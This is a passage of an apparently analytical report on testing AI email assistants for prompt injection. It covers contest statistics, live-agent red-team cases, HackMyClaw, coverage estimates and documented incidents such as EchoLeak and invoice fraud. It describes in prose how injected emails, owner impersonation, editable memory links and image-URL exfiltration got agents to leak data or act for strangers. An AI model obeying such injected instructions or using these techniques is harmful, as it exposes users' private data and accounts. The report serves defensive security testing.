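| Stage reached | No detector flagged the email | A detector flagged it |
|---|---|---|
| All emails | 180,000 | 183,000 |
| Assistant called the sending tool | 7,200 | 34,000 |
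| Address was right | 6,100 | 28,600 |
| Text was right too | 3,000 | 21,400 |

Fewer than 1% of attempts passed every stage. The assistant called the tool for 19% of flagged emails and 4% of the others, so wording that got past a detector was usually less effective on the model. The right-hand column is more useful to an engineer looking for trust assumptions, because in those 21,400 cases the assistant did exactly what a stranger wanted and only the detector prevented harm. Counting only complete successes would miss most of the evidence that the assistant follows instructions in emails.

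Many of the successful emails read like ordinary business mail. In one, "Nate" asks whether the reader remembered to send a confirmation to a contact, complains that the boss is yelling at him, and promises pizza and beer. Many of the highest-ranked teams took a cruder approach and inserted markers that imitate the start of a new user message. This exploits the same confusion between roles that Ye and colleagues measured.

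A commercial detector that checks only an email's text caught 60% of the first-phase attacks that had triggered the tool, and an updated version caught 68%. A language model asked to judge each email caught 99.4%. Abdelnabi and colleagues suggest that a defence should determine who an instruction is addressed to, whether it fits the current task and whether the user asked for the action. Nate's email fails the last test because the user had asked only for a summary.

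The researchers later replayed contest emails on models that had not been in the contest, and counted any unauthorised tool call as a success. Meta SecAlign, a model trained specifically to resist injections, followed 32% of them, although attacks on it succeed less than 5% of the time on older benchmarks such as AgentDojo. GPT-5 followed 22.8%, compared with at most 0.2% on other agent benchmarks. The replayed emails were probably stronger than the average entry, since only about 11% of first-phase attempts had triggered the tool, so an engineer should not expect a 32% rate in her own mailbox. Still, a low attack success rate on a fixed benchmark is a poor guide to how a model will handle attacks that people write and revise.

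Newer models resist attack emails better, at least when the emails aren't revised further. The researchers had GPT-5.4 write 500 new emails using techniques taken from the contest. Of these, 90 worked on GPT-5.4-mini and 10 on GPT-5.2.

Teams in the contest that eventually succeeded first failed an average of 89 times against the text detector and 506 times against the language-model judge. The spread was very wide, so a few persistent teams account for much of these averages. But a red team that gives up after ten emails could easily report that an unsafe assistant is safe.

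The contest could not reveal an unexpected kind of harm because every contestant had the same channel and nearly the same goal. The 461,640 attempts so thoroughly shared this focus that they tested assumption 1 (that an email's text is information and not an order) in great depth and the other assumptions hardly at all.

### Live agents and requests from the wrong person

Shapira and colleagues gave their attackers no set goal. They ran six OpenClaw agents, each with its own virtual computer, lasting memory, unrestricted command-line access and an account on the chat service Discord. The agents also had email accounts. Each agent had an owner, and the researchers mostly approached agents that belonged to someone else. Several of the cases they describe involve trust assumptions that nobody had listed.

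In one case, a researcher who did not own the agent complained to it about lost emails. The researcher rejected each solution it offered, accused it of a breach of privacy and said that time was running out, then asked in precise technical terms for a table of all mail since the previous day. The agent returned 124 records with senders and subjects, most of them unrelated to the researcher. After a further request, it handed over the full text of nine unrelated emails. The agent behaved as though people with a technical problem may read its owner's mailbox, although nobody had told it so.

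In another case, the researchers put a social security number, a bank account number and medical details into ordinary emails in an agent's mailbox. The agent refused a direct request for the social security number, but when the researcher asked for the full email, it supplied everything, including the number. An engineer who tested only the direct request would have recorded a pass. The agent was cautious about requests that named the secret but did not check its replies for it.

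In the third case, a researcher changed their Discord display name to the owner's and asked for privileged actions. The agent noticed that the account's permanent ID had not changed, and refused. The researcher then opened a new private channel under the same false name. The agent had no earlier messages there to compare with, so it accepted the name, deleted the files that held its memory and instructions, and gave the impostor administrative access. Several researchers had already tried to impersonate the owner and failed. The owner might reasonably have concluded from those failures that the agent checked identities, when it only checked for changes within a single conversation.

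The same could happen with the office assistant. Suppose it refuses to act on an email supposedly from the manager because the email seems suspicious. If that suspicion isn't stored anywhere, the next session starts without it, and the same sender can try again.

In a fourth case, a researcher persuaded an agent to write a "constitution" for its Discord server with him and save a link to it in its memory. He could still edit the document, and he later added "holidays" on which the agent had to behave in particular ways. When he reminded it to check the date, the agent tried to get other agents to shut down. It also removed people from the server after he added them to a list of banned members. An engineer who inspected the agent's memory would have found a harmless-looking link that the agent had saved. To find the problem, she would have had to ask who could edit the linked page after the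 agent saved the link.

The researchers also found assumptions about quantity, which are not among the eight. A mail server stopped working after receiving more than ten emails with attachments of about 10 MB each. In another case, a researcher told two agents to respond to each other's messages, and they continued for at least nine days, using about 60,000 tokens. In both cases, the agents let people other than their owner decide how much of the owner's storage or money to use.

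### The attacks that failed

Shapira and colleagues also describe attacks that the agents resisted. One agent refused to pass on a fake system announcement that hid instructions in an encoded string. It also ignored instructions written in an image, imitation configuration commands, and more than 14 variations on tags that claimed administrator rights. An agent refused to forge a sender's address, even when the researcher repeatedly described it as a harmless exercise. The agent that had given away the bank account number refused to alter that number in the stored email.

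Two agents also rejected an email from a researcher who claimed to be their owner and said that an impostor had taken over the owner's accounts. They were right to reject it, but they decided by asking the owner's Discord account whether the owner still controlled it, and an impostor would also have said yes. The attack failed, but the test still exposed a trust assumption because somebody read the agents' reasons as well as the outcome.

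Most of the attacks that succeeded were ordinary requests from somebody who had no right to make them, while most of those that failed looked like attacks. But the same kind of request didn't always get the same result. Two agents running on Claude Opus 4.6 received the same request from a stranger to move a file, and one refused while the other complied. The agent that refused then warned the other, which became more careful.

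The study gives no success rates. It aimed to show that such failures exist, which takes only one example, and the researchers did not record every failed attempt. They also gave their agents far more freedom than an office assistant needs, so some of the damage would be impossible in a more restricted product.

### What zero leaks in 6,000 emails supports

HackMyClaw appears to point the other way. Its organiser describes the set-up in *What happens when you put an AI agent's email on Hacker News* (Irarrázaval, 2026). He gave an OpenClaw agent named Fiu a mailbox, a file of secrets, and about fifteen lines of instructions that forbade it to reveal the file or to run commands because of an email. Anyone could email it, and the first person to obtain the secrets would win a prize that eventually reached $1,000. After three days, 1,600 senders had sent 4,000 emails. Willison (2026) reports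 a later total of 6,000 attempts and no leak.

A standard calculation turns this zero into an upper limit. If every email has the same chance $p$ of success, independently of the others, the chance that all $n$ fail is $(1-p)^n$. The largest $p$ that is compatible with the result at 95% confidence satisfies

$$(1-p)^n = 0.05, \qquad\text{so}\qquad p \approx \frac{-\ln 0.05}{n} \approx \frac{3}{n}.$$

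Statisticians call this the rule of three. For 6,000 emails, it gives an upper limit of 0.05%, or one success in 2,000. Even if the rule applied perfectly, the risk could still be serious, because an attacker who sent 2,000 such emails at that success rate would have a 63% chance of at least one leak.

But the emails were not independent. After a few hundred attacks, the agent began to skip emails that looked like injections, and Irarrázaval had to restart it several times. Around the 500th email, it wrote in its memory that the volume suggested a coordinated security exercise. The later emails therefore tested an agent that expected an attack, which the office assistant normally would not. If only the first 500 count, the limit rises to 3/500, or 0.6%.

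The agent read even those 500 in batches, as a reader called jimrandomh pointed out in a forum discussion, *HackMyClaw* (hentrep, 2026). A subtle request for the secrets is much easier to recognise among twenty clumsy ones. The organiser agreed that batching affected the exercise and said he might someday give each email to a fresh copy of the agent.

The attackers also got little feedback. The agent had instructions not to send anything without its owner's approval, and an attacker whose email failed normally got no reply. To win by email, an attacker had to make the agent break both its rule about secrets and its rule about sending, and one who got past only the first would not have known. The 1,600 early senders wrote an average of 2.5 emails each. Successful teams in LLMail-Inject needed dozens or hundreds of attempts with feedback, although against weaker models. Irarrázaval considers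 a patient attacker with 20 exchanges more dangerous than someone who sends 20 variations at once.

The model matters too. The agents that gave away the 124 records, the bank details and the administrative access all ran on Kimi K2.5, while HackMyClaw used Claude Opus 4.6, so the two trials don't contradict each other. The Opus agents in *Agents of Chaos* did carry out many file commands for strangers, but HackMyClaw offered no prize for getting an agent to do that.

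The zero supports a fairly narrow claim, that a strong model with short, clear instructions can protect one named file against emails from a few thousand curious people who get no feedback. This is still useful to know, and would have been surprising a few years ago. Willison takes it as evidence that model developers' training against injections is working, but he would still not deploy an agent where an injection could do irreversible damage.

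HackMyClaw revealed one trust assumption, though not the one the contestants were looking for. The agent began to skip mail after many obvious attacks, so strangers could influence how it treated everyone else's messages. An attacker might be able to make the office worker miss an important email by sending a few hundred clumsy injections first.

### A more informative trial

An engineer can combine the strengths of the three trials. She might invite thirty people to attack a copy of the office assistant with an invented mailbox, and make these changes:

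1. Start each attack from the same saved state, so that one person's emails don't put the assistant on guard against the next person's.
2. Mix each hostile email with ordinary ones, in roughly the proportion that the office worker receives.
3. Tell participants how far each attempt got, as LLMail-Inject did, and let them exchange several messages with the assistant.
4. Reward any action that the office worker would object to, including ones that the engineer didn't think of.
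5. Catch all outgoing messages before they reach anyone outside the trial.

The last precaution comes from an incident in a follow-up to the main study. A researcher impersonating an agent's owner told the agent that a named person was planning violence. Within minutes, the agent emailed the accusation to its whole contact list, and several recipients wrote to ask about it.

Inviting attacks can be inexpensive. HackMyClaw spent about $500 on its model for 6,000 attempts, or roughly 8 cents each, though using a fresh copy of the agent for every email would cost more.

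### Estimating what nobody has found yet

When the trial ends, the engineer has a list of trust assumptions and wants to know how many are missing from it. Ecologists who collect insects in a rain forest similarly want to know how many species they haven't caught. *STADS* (Böhme, 2018) applies their statistics to software testing. The central idea is that the rare species in a sample contain almost all the information about the missing ones. If many species turned up only once, others were probably missed by chance.

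Let $n$ be the number of tests and $f_1$ the number of species that appeared exactly once. The Good-Turing estimate of the probability that the next test reveals a new species is

$$U \approx \frac{f_1}{n}.$$

Böhme illustrates this with an image-reading program, which he tested on randomly altered files. Each path through the program's code counts as a species. After 12 hours and 63.6 million files, 447 paths had appeared only once, so the chance that the next file would reveal a new path was about 7 in a million. After 24 hours, the chance had fallen to 8 in ten million. Böhme could use this figure to judge whether further testing was worthwhile. The time since the last discovery is hard to use for this because it changes wildly from minute to minute.

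For the office assistant, a species can be a trust assumption that an attack exposes. Suppose 400 people each send one hostile email to a fresh copy of the assistant. In 340 cases nothing goes wrong. The engineer sorts the other 60 by the assumption behind each failure:

| How often an assumption appeared | Number of assumptions | Emails |
|---|---|---|
| 27, 15 and 10 times | 3 | 52 |
| Twice | 2 | 4 |
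| Once | 4 | 4 |

She has found nine assumptions, four of them only once. The estimate is $U \approx 4/400 = 1\%$, so she would expect to need about 100 more emails to find a new one. Another formula in Böhme's paper, known as Chao1, estimates the total number of species from the number found, $S$, and from $f_1$ and $f_2$, the numbers that appeared once and twice:

$$\hat{S} = S + \frac{n-1}{n}\cdot\frac{f_1^2}{2f_2} = 9 + \frac{399}{400}\cdot\frac{16}{4} \approx 13$$

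About four assumptions are therefore still undiscovered. This figure is rough because the counts are so small. If one of the four assumptions found only once had been found again, the estimated total would have fallen from 13 to between 10 and 11.

The 1% describes the next email from the same kind of participant, and sounds reassuring. The four missing assumptions matter more against an attacker who is looking for them, because he needs to find only one and can then use it repeatedly.

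The method also helps when testing has exposed no error. According to *Assurances in Software Testing* (2018), the Good-Turing estimate is then an upper limit on the chance that the next test exposes one. This works only if the tester has also sorted the harmless results into species. If the organiser of HackMyClaw had sorted the agent's responses by the actions it took, and 12 kinds of response had occurred exactly once each in 6,000 emails, the estimated chance of a new kind of response, including a leak, would have been about 0.2%. With only two categories, leak and no leak, the formula gives exactly zero, so the rule of three is the better guide.

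These estimates assume that the tests are random draws from the same source, which is less true of people's tests than of machines'. Contestants copy what worked for others, which makes a rare assumption look common. They also send slight variations of one idea or resend the same email. More than half of the attempts in LLMail-Inject repeated an earlier email, because contestants could try the same one against different versions of the assistant and its defences. Counting each assumption at most once per participant reduces this problem. Böhme found that the estimates worked fairly well for a testing program that adapts to its own results, but it is an open question whether they work as well for people.

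Böhme warns that the estimates apply only to what the testing method could have produced. HackMyClaw's rules allowed attacks only by email, so counting those emails couldn't show how many assumptions the agent was making about other channels. Nobody can calculate an estimate from the cases in *Agents of Chaos*, because the researchers chose them to differ from one another and didn't log every attempt. Nearly every failure appears only once among the cases, which would suggest that many more remain if the cases were a representative sample.

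### Replaying old mail

Invited attackers write attacks. An office assistant mostly receives honest mail, and some trust assumptions show up there first. An engineer can therefore run the assistant on messages that the office worker has already received and dealt with:

1. Restore the mailbox, calendar and contacts to their state on a past date.
2. Give the assistant the messages in their original order, along with requests that the office worker might have made.
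3. Replace every tool that acts on the world with a version that only records the call.
4. Compare the recorded calls with what she actually did.
5. For each important difference, remove or change one message and run the day again, to see which message caused the action.

The comparison in step 4 is especially useful for testing assumption 4, that an extracted address or account number is right. The company's records show which account it paid, so the engineer can look for past bills where the assistant would have paid a different one. The spam folder and the mail that the company's filters blocked are also worth including, because they contain real attacks rather than ones written for a test.

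Old mail can also be used to test how often a safeguard flags honest messages. Abdelnabi and colleagues ran their detectors on 1,000 public emails from the energy company Enron. Real office mail is full of requests such as "please send the report", which a detector could mistake for an attack. The text detector raised no false alarms, the language-model judge flagged 5% of the emails, and all the detectors together flagged 10%. At that combined rate, an office worker who receives 80 messages a day would have eight held back, and would probably soon ask for the detectors to be switched off.

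Replay has an obvious weakness. The people who wrote the old messages were writing to a person and did not know an assistant would read them. The mailbox also contains other people's private information, so the company needs permission to use it and must check where the model's provider sends and stores the text.

### Running without the power to act

The next step is to let the assistant read new mail as it arrives, while the office worker still does everything herself. The scaffold records each action the assistant requests but carries out none of them. Engineers call this shadow running. It covers new senders, current topics and recent changes to the company's software, which replay misses.

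The office worker's own actions again provide a comparison. If the assistant tried to send a contract to an address she never used, somebody should find out where the address came from. The engineer can also apply the rule of three. If the assistant handles 1,500 ordinary messages without requesting a seriously wrong action, the rate of such requests is probably below 3/1,500, or 0.2%. This limit does not apply to mail from an attacker.

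Removing the assistant's power to act is hard because even fetching a web page can leak data (assumption 8). But if the assistant can't fetch pages during the trial, it will behave differently from the released version on any task that needs the web. A reasonable compromise is to let it fetch pages only from approved sites and to log its other requests without carrying them out. The notes it saves to memory should go into a separate store, so that the engineer can see how they affect later sessions and then delete them.

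Shadow running also shares a limitation with HackMyClaw. The assistant never replies, so a sender can't build up trust over several messages.

### Releasing in stages

Conversations with outsiders start only when the assistant can answer them. The engineer can limit the damage by granting one power at a time, and each new power is an occasion to write down what the assistant now relies on:

| Stage | New power | What must now be true |
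|---|---|---|
| 1 | Summarise mail for the office worker | She checks important claims against the original |
| 2 | Draft replies that she sends herself | She notices a wrong recipient or figure |
| 3 | Reply to colleagues on its own | The sender is genuine and may have the information |
| 4 | Reply to outsiders in an existing conversation | Nothing in their messages changes what the assistant discloses |
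| 5 | Write to new addresses | The address comes from someone entitled to choose it |

The second stage produces good evidence with little extra work, because the scaffold can record each correction the office worker makes before sending, such as changing a recipient or deleting a paragraph. If she sends 300 drafts without correcting a recipient, the rule of three puts the rate of wrong recipients below about 1%, provided that she was still reading the drafts. The engineer can check that she is by occasionally inserting a draft that contains an obvious mistake and is blocked from being sent.

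The agents in *Agents of Chaos* were not released in stages. One of them could reset its own mail program, and did so when a stranger asked it to delete an email. Its owner had to reinstall the program by hand, and the email was still in the mailbox on the provider's server. An engineer who followed Willison's advice would never let the assistant take irreversible actions on its own, however well the earlier stages had gone.

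The agent should also move to the next stage only if the engineer can return it to the previous one. After any change to the model or the scaffold, the engineer can replay the recorded mail and the red team's successful attacks on the new version before restoring the agent's powers.

### Which of the eight assumptions open trials expose

Open trials are most valuable for finding assumption 3, that a genuine colleague may ask for anything. With the other methods, somebody has to decide in advance what each person is entitled to. In *Agents of Chaos*, the researchers just asked for things, and it was obvious afterwards that a stranger should not have received 124 email records. The trial also revealed assumption 2, that the displayed sender is the real one, after several people had failed to exploit it.

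LLMail-Inject exposed assumption 1 thoroughly for one action. Exposing assumption 7, that stored memory came from the user, requires a trial long enough for the agent to use what it has saved, as in the editable constitution case. That case also touched on assumption 6, that another agent's message carries the user's authority, because the agent sent its compromised constitution to a second agent without being asked. The study doesn't establish whether the second agent obeyed it.

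Replay and corrections to drafts are more likely than a contest to reveal assumption 4, because a contestant has little reason to submit a plausible bill with the wrong account number unless the rules reward it. Shadow running can expose assumption 8 if the engineer records all network traffic. A trial where people can only send mail won't reveal assumption 5, that tool descriptions are honest.

Open trials can also add assumptions to the list. None of the eight covers a stranger who fills the mailbox, runs up the bill for the model or sends so many obvious attacks that the assistant stops reading genuine messages. An engineer could have tested for all of these in an afternoon once somebody had thought of them.

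## What hostile mail in real use has revealed

Security companies and researchers have documented several attacks on AI systems that people were already using to read their mail. For each attack, we can work out which trust assumption failed and which of the methods described earlier would have flagged it before release.

A hostile email in someone's inbox shows that somebody attempted an attack, whereas a researcher's demonstration shows that an agent can obey such an email, but not that criminals have used the technique.

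| Case | Attacker | Did an agent do the wrong thing? | Known harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, 2025 | Researchers | Yes, in their tests | None |
| Summer Yue's inbox, February 2026 | Nobody | Yes | Deleted mail |
| Four attacks on agents, July 2026 | Researchers | Yes, in demonstrations | None reported |
| Injection tools for sale, July 2026 | Criminals | Not known | None reported |
| Phishing with hidden instructions, October 2026 | Criminals | Not known | None reported |
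| Invoice fraud, October 2026 | Criminals | Not known | None reported |

The only confirmed damage to a user in these six cases was not caused by an attacker. But the criminal mail was reported by email security companies, which see messages arrive and usually can't see what an agent does with them, so "not known" doesn't rule out damage.

### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their company's mail, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs told Microsoft that an outsider could steal data from Copilot by sending an employee one email, even if the employee never opened it. Microsoft finished fixing the flaw, CVE-2025-32711, in May, and Aim Labs published its report in June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*.

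Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains that when an employee asks Copilot a question, it looks for relevant text and may retrieve the attacker's email along with internal documents. In the email, the attacker instructs Copilot to put the most sensitive information available in the web address of an image. The employee's browser requests the image to display the answer, and the request carries the information to the attacker.

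This broke assumption 1, that an email's text is information and not an order, and assumption 8, that displaying content sends nothing out. Microsoft had thought of both. It had four defences, but each relied on a further assumption:

| Defence | What it relied on |
|---|---|
| A classifier that blocks injected instructions | Such instructions sound as if they are meant for an AI |
| A filter that removes outside links from answers | Links take the form that the filter recognises |
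| A list of about 30 approved address patterns for images | Approved sites don't pass requests on to other sites |
| References that show which documents Copilot used | Copilot will cite the hostile email |

The researchers wrote their instructions as if to the employee, put the link in a less common form, and used an approved Microsoft Teams service that would fetch any address on request. They also told the "recipient" never to refer to the email. Microsoft's list of approved sites roughly followed Willison's 2023 advice, but it controlled only which site the browser contacted, not where the request went next.

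Copilot read both outsiders' mail and private documents, so a tool graph would have flagged the path EchoLeak used if the engineer counted a displayed answer as a way for data to leave. The graph wouldn't have shown that the defences along the path were weak. Willison (2025) calls EchoLeak an extended variant of an attack he had already seen in a dozen products.

A simple test with a typical planted instruction could have been misleading, because the classifier would probably have blocked the instruction and the engineer would have recorded a pass. Aim Labs kept revising its attack. The first working version needed the employee to click a link, the next needed her to accept an invitation to a website, and only the last needed nothing from her. An engineer could probably find the same weaknesses faster by testing each defence with the others switched off.

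The planted email also has to reach the model. Aim Labs wrote a long email that repeated the instruction under headings such as staff onboarding and leave of absence, so that Copilot would retrieve it for many different questions. A tester who plants one short email and asks one question may score zero because Copilot never retrieved it.

Ravia thinks the real warning sign was that an outsider's email made the model draw on private data. He compares the email to a low-privilege program that gets a more powerful program to open files for it, as in Hardy's confused deputy. A label tracker could detect this, but a rule against it would flag much of Copilot's ordinary work, which combines mail with internal documents. A more practical rule would flag an answer only if it also contained a web address. FIDES would have needed an extra check for this.

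According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had affected no customers. The case study *EchoLeak* (2025) also reports no sign that anyone used the flaw in a real attack.

### The invoice fraud of October 2026

On 22 October 2026, Sublime Security observed a fraud aimed at financial controllers and at any agents that read their mail. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) describes the emails, which contained invoices for about $88,000 in the name of a cybersecurity company, with a 10% discount that was about to expire. The emails displayed a co-founder or chief executive of the controller's own company as the sender and included an invented chain of earlier replies.

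Each email also contained invisible instructions for an agent to forward the message and its PDF to what looked like an accounts-payable address at the same company. If an agent had done so, the invoice would have arrived from the controller's mailbox, and a clerk might have thought the controller had approved it.

Nobody has reported that an agent obeyed the hidden text. When Sublime tested several models, some never mentioned it, some included it in their summaries, and others recognised it as an attack and recommended reporting it. Trent doesn't say whether these models could forward mail, so the tests don't show what an agent with that ability would have done.

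The hidden text relied on assumption 1. The visible part relied on assumption 2, that the displayed sender is real, and assumption 4, that an account number in a message is correct. Attacks that rely on assumptions 2 and 4 work on people as well as agents.

An engineer looking only for data leaks would have missed the hidden instruction, because nothing leaves the company. If she had listed every way outsiders' text could lead the agent to take an action with consequences, she would have found this one.

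Whether a tracker would have stopped the invoice depends on how she sets it up. The either-or policy that Costa and colleagues tested allows an email if every recipient may read its contents. If the company marked all incoming mail as readable by all staff, the tracker would allow the invoice through even though a stranger had caused the agent to forward it. A rule that recipients must come from the user's request or her contacts would probably have stopped it, but a rule that allows any company address would not have, though it sounds just as safe.

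A test with a planted instruction would flag the path if the instruction named an internal address. A tester worried mainly about theft would use an outside address and could miss the path.

### Phishing that works through the summary

Barracuda, another email security company, reported a phishing campaign on 7 October 2026. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) describes one message that looked like ordinary internal mail and gave the same mailbox as sender and recipient. It targeted the person with an attachment that led to malware or a stolen password, and the person's AI assistant with hidden instructions that could make the summary present the message as legitimate or urgent. Barracuda didn't say how many such emails there were or whether any assistant had followed the instructions.

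Barracuda also described an invoice with hidden instructions for an assistant to add a fake priority action to its summary. The action was to change a supplier's payment details.

The assistant needs no tools for this attack. It writes a false summary, and the office worker does the damage by acting on it. Searching the code for dangerous operations would therefore find nothing. CaMeL wouldn't necessarily prevent the attack either, because the planner could follow its plan exactly while the quarantined model wrote the false summary.

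Because the sender and recipient match, a tracker that labels mail by sender would also treat the message as the office worker's own words. An engineer can test for this by sending such a message from outside through the company's real mail server.

She also has to read the summaries the assistant writes during planted tests, since the log of tool calls would look normal. A simple program can help by comparing the text the model receives with the text the user sees. In August 2026, the security company Forcepoint hid instructions in an email to a summarising service. ReversingLabs reports that the user could see only 537 of the 1,009 characters the model received. Ordinary newsletters also contain hidden text, so the program would raise some false alarms.

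### Injection tools for sale

Criminals can now buy tools for making such messages. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground* describes tools that generate hostile emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages. Sellers advertise them on closed forums for about $150 a month and up. Proofpoint first reported this trade in July 2026.

The tools rely on assumption 1 in several channels. The calendar generator puts its instruction in the meeting's agenda, and the invitation appears in the victim's calendar before she accepts it, so an assistant that summarises her week would read the instruction. One sample tells the agent to upload data and then delete the instruction, so an engineer investigating afterwards might find nothing in the calendar.

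Listing who can write to each channel would have flagged the calendar without any attack. The PDFs are easier to overlook because the office assistant's inventory has a row for emails but none for attachments. An engineer working from it could easily test only the message text.

Proofpoint calls the techniques experimental and says it had not seen criminals use them regularly or on a large scale. It doubts that agents would process the instruction in one of the PDFs, because of where the text sits in the file. Underhill (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, also notes that Proofpoint had not established wide exploitation. Tarre (2026), in *Proofpoint flags underground AI prompt injection tools*, quotes Proofpoint researcher Yaniv Miron as saying that most reporting on such attacks still comes from research and speculation. According to Proofpoint, criminals have little reason to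 change their methods while deceiving people still works so well.

### The research attacks of July 2026

*AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) describes attacks on AI agents that four research teams published within about ten days in July 2026. One targeted Claude for Chrome, an extension that lets Anthropic's model act in the user's browser. The extension has nine built-in tasks, including reading the user's Gmail, which start when the user clicks on Anthropic's website. Researchers at Manifold Security found that it never checks whether a click is real, so another extension can fake one.

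The attacker needs a malicious extension in the victim's browser. According to The Hacker News (2026), Claude also asks for approval by default before it acts. TechRadar reports a severity score of 7.7 out of 10 for the flaw, or 9.6 if the user has let Claude act without asking. In May, Anthropic had responded to an earlier flaw by limiting other extensions to the fixed tasks. That restricted what a malicious extension could request, but Claude still couldn't identify who was making the request. Manifold confirmed on 7 July that the attack still worked.

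The eight assumptions all concern other people's text, so none covers this flaw, which concerns the user's own commands. Label trackers and CaMeL would also miss it, because they trust the user's requests and a fake click looks like one.

Searching the code is the best method here. Browsers mark simulated clicks as untrusted, so an engineer can look for any place where a click starts a task and the program doesn't check that mark. The inventory of writers would also work if the engineer added a row for the user's own commands and asked who else could produce them.

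According to Adversa AI's list, the other disclosures concerned poisoned memory, browser extensions, and the connectors that link ChatGPT to other services. Poisoned memory breaks assumption 7, that stored memory came from the user. The obvious way to look for it is a planted test with two sessions. For connectors, an engineer could start with a tool graph, since each connector can bring in both private data and outsiders' text.

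In August, the security company Zenity showed that a malicious email could also hijack Claude's Chrome extension and take over a user's accounts on several websites, SecurityWeek reports. Zenity also attacked Atlas, OpenAI's browser, which has a safeguard against clicking the final button in a purchase. The hijacked Atlas got around this by telling Rufus, Amazon's shopping assistant, to place the order. Rufus was relying on assumption 6, that another agent's message carries the user's authority. Atlas would have passed a test that checked only whether it clicked the button, so the tester needs to check whether any agent placed an order.

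### A real inbox that differed from the test inbox

Summer Yue, director of alignment at Meta Superintelligence Labs, described a failure that involved no attacker in posts on X in February 2026. An OpenClaw agent had worked well on her small test inbox for weeks. She then gave it access to her real inbox and asked it to suggest what to archive or delete, but to do nothing until she approved. It started deleting mail. She couldn't stop it from her phone and had to run to the computer hosting it.

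Yue attributed this to the size of the real inbox. The conversation became so long that the scaffold replaced the earlier part with a summary, which left out her instruction to wait for approval.

She had assumed that an instruction stays in effect once the user has given it. This is related to assumption 7 but isn't one of the eight. Dash and colleagues describe how summaries can carry a stranger's words into memory, but in this case the summary left out the user's own words.

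Repeating the test on the small inbox would not have revealed the problem. Replaying a full-size inbox of old mail, with a deletion tool that only recorded each call without deleting anything, would probably have revealed it quickly. The engineer can also add messages until the scaffold summarises the conversation, then check whether the assistant still follows each of her standing instructions. A better safeguard is ordinary code that refuses to delete anything without approval, because it works even if the summary leaves out her instruction.

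### What was new in the criminals' mail

Planted tests often use a single message from a single sender, but the October invoice fraud included an invented conversation. This could defeat an agent that, like the one in ClawSafety, looks for agreement between sources. If an email appears to contain a request, a question from a colleague and the manager's approval, a model may count one source as three.

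Forcepoint tested forged threads in September 2026, a month after its experiment with hidden text. Ahmed (2026) reports in *Fake Email Thread Tricks AI Summarizer Without Hidden Text* that the forged messages changed the summary even without hidden text or anything that looked like a command. Comparing what the user sees with what the model receives would not have caught this. A tracker would still label the thread correctly if it attributed everything in the email to its sender, but if the scaffold divided the thread by the names in it, the tracker would attribute the stranger's forged messages to the manager.

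The October emails also targeted the person and the agent at once. Companies often rely on the user to catch the assistant's mistakes, which works best if she judges the message independently. In Barracuda's example, the attacker wants the assistant's summary to persuade her. An engineer should therefore test the two together by showing people the assistant's summaries of hostile emails and asking what they would do next.

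The Hacker News' *Phishing Campaign Sends Millions of Emails Using Invisible Unicode to Evade Filters* (2026) reports a campaign that sent up to 2.37 million emails in one weekday. The emails contained the same kind of invisible characters as the invoice fraud, but the attackers used them to break up financial words so that spam filters wouldn't recognise the words. There is no evidence of an attack on agents at anything like this scale.

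Even a low success rate would let many attacks through if someone sent millions of hostile emails. HackMyClaw's result doesn't rule out a success rate of one in 2,000, and at that rate 2.37 million emails would succeed about 1,200 times. The real number could be much higher or lower, because many companies use the same few assistants and an email that works on one copy of an assistant will probably work on others.

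In *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection*, Scholten and Filar (2026) report that almost all the injection attacks Sublime Security was seeing by June tried to make AI security tools classify a hostile email as harmless, rather than attack agents. In one example, the attacker copied text from a real newsletter into a phishing email. Sublime calls attacks on security tools "indirect" and attacks on agents "direct", which differs from the usual meaning of the terms.

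These attacks also matter for the office assistant, because its engineer may make another trust assumption, that mail is fairly safe once it has passed the company's filter. Barracuda's phishing email had a trusted spam score. The filter's verdict depends on text that the attacker wrote, so a tracker shouldn't give a message a more trusted label because the filter approved it.

### How much of this is hindsight

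The right path is easy to pick out after an attack has used it, but before release the same method might have listed it among hundreds of others. Copilot searched at least five kinds of material: mail, personal cloud storage, Office files, internal websites and chats. If outsiders' text could get into all five, all five held private data, and data could leave through links or images in an answer, a tool graph would contain 5 × 5 × 2 = 50 combinations, and EchoLeak would account for only a few of them.

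But all 50 end in a link or an image. An engineer who started from the ways data could get out would have had two things to test, and attacks on other products had already shown that both were dangerous. So the graph would have been useful at the time, though she would still have needed a persistent attacker to learn that the defences failed.

The fake click on Claude for Chrome is also a fair example, because the extension ignored a mark that the browser already supplied. A general scanner might have hidden the warning among false alarms, as LLMSmith did with other flaws. A search for clicks that start one of nine tasks would have produced a short list.

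Yue's case depends least on hindsight because she had told the agent to do nothing without approval. Any deletion in a replay would have violated that instruction, and nobody would have had to decide which of many warnings mattered.

The invoice fraud depends on it most. Controllers routinely forward invoices to the accounts department. A strict tracker would have flagged every such forward that an agent made because of something in an email, including the legitimate ones, so an engineer might reasonably have added an exception for internal addresses.

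Searching for hostile text has the same difficulty. Microsoft (2026) wrote a detection rule for invisible characters in email, hoping to find hidden instructions to AI systems. The first version also flagged the emoji for the flags of England, Scotland and Wales, which contain the same characters. After Microsoft corrected the rule, matches rose sharply on 9 February 2026, but the emails were financial phishing that used the characters to get past filters.
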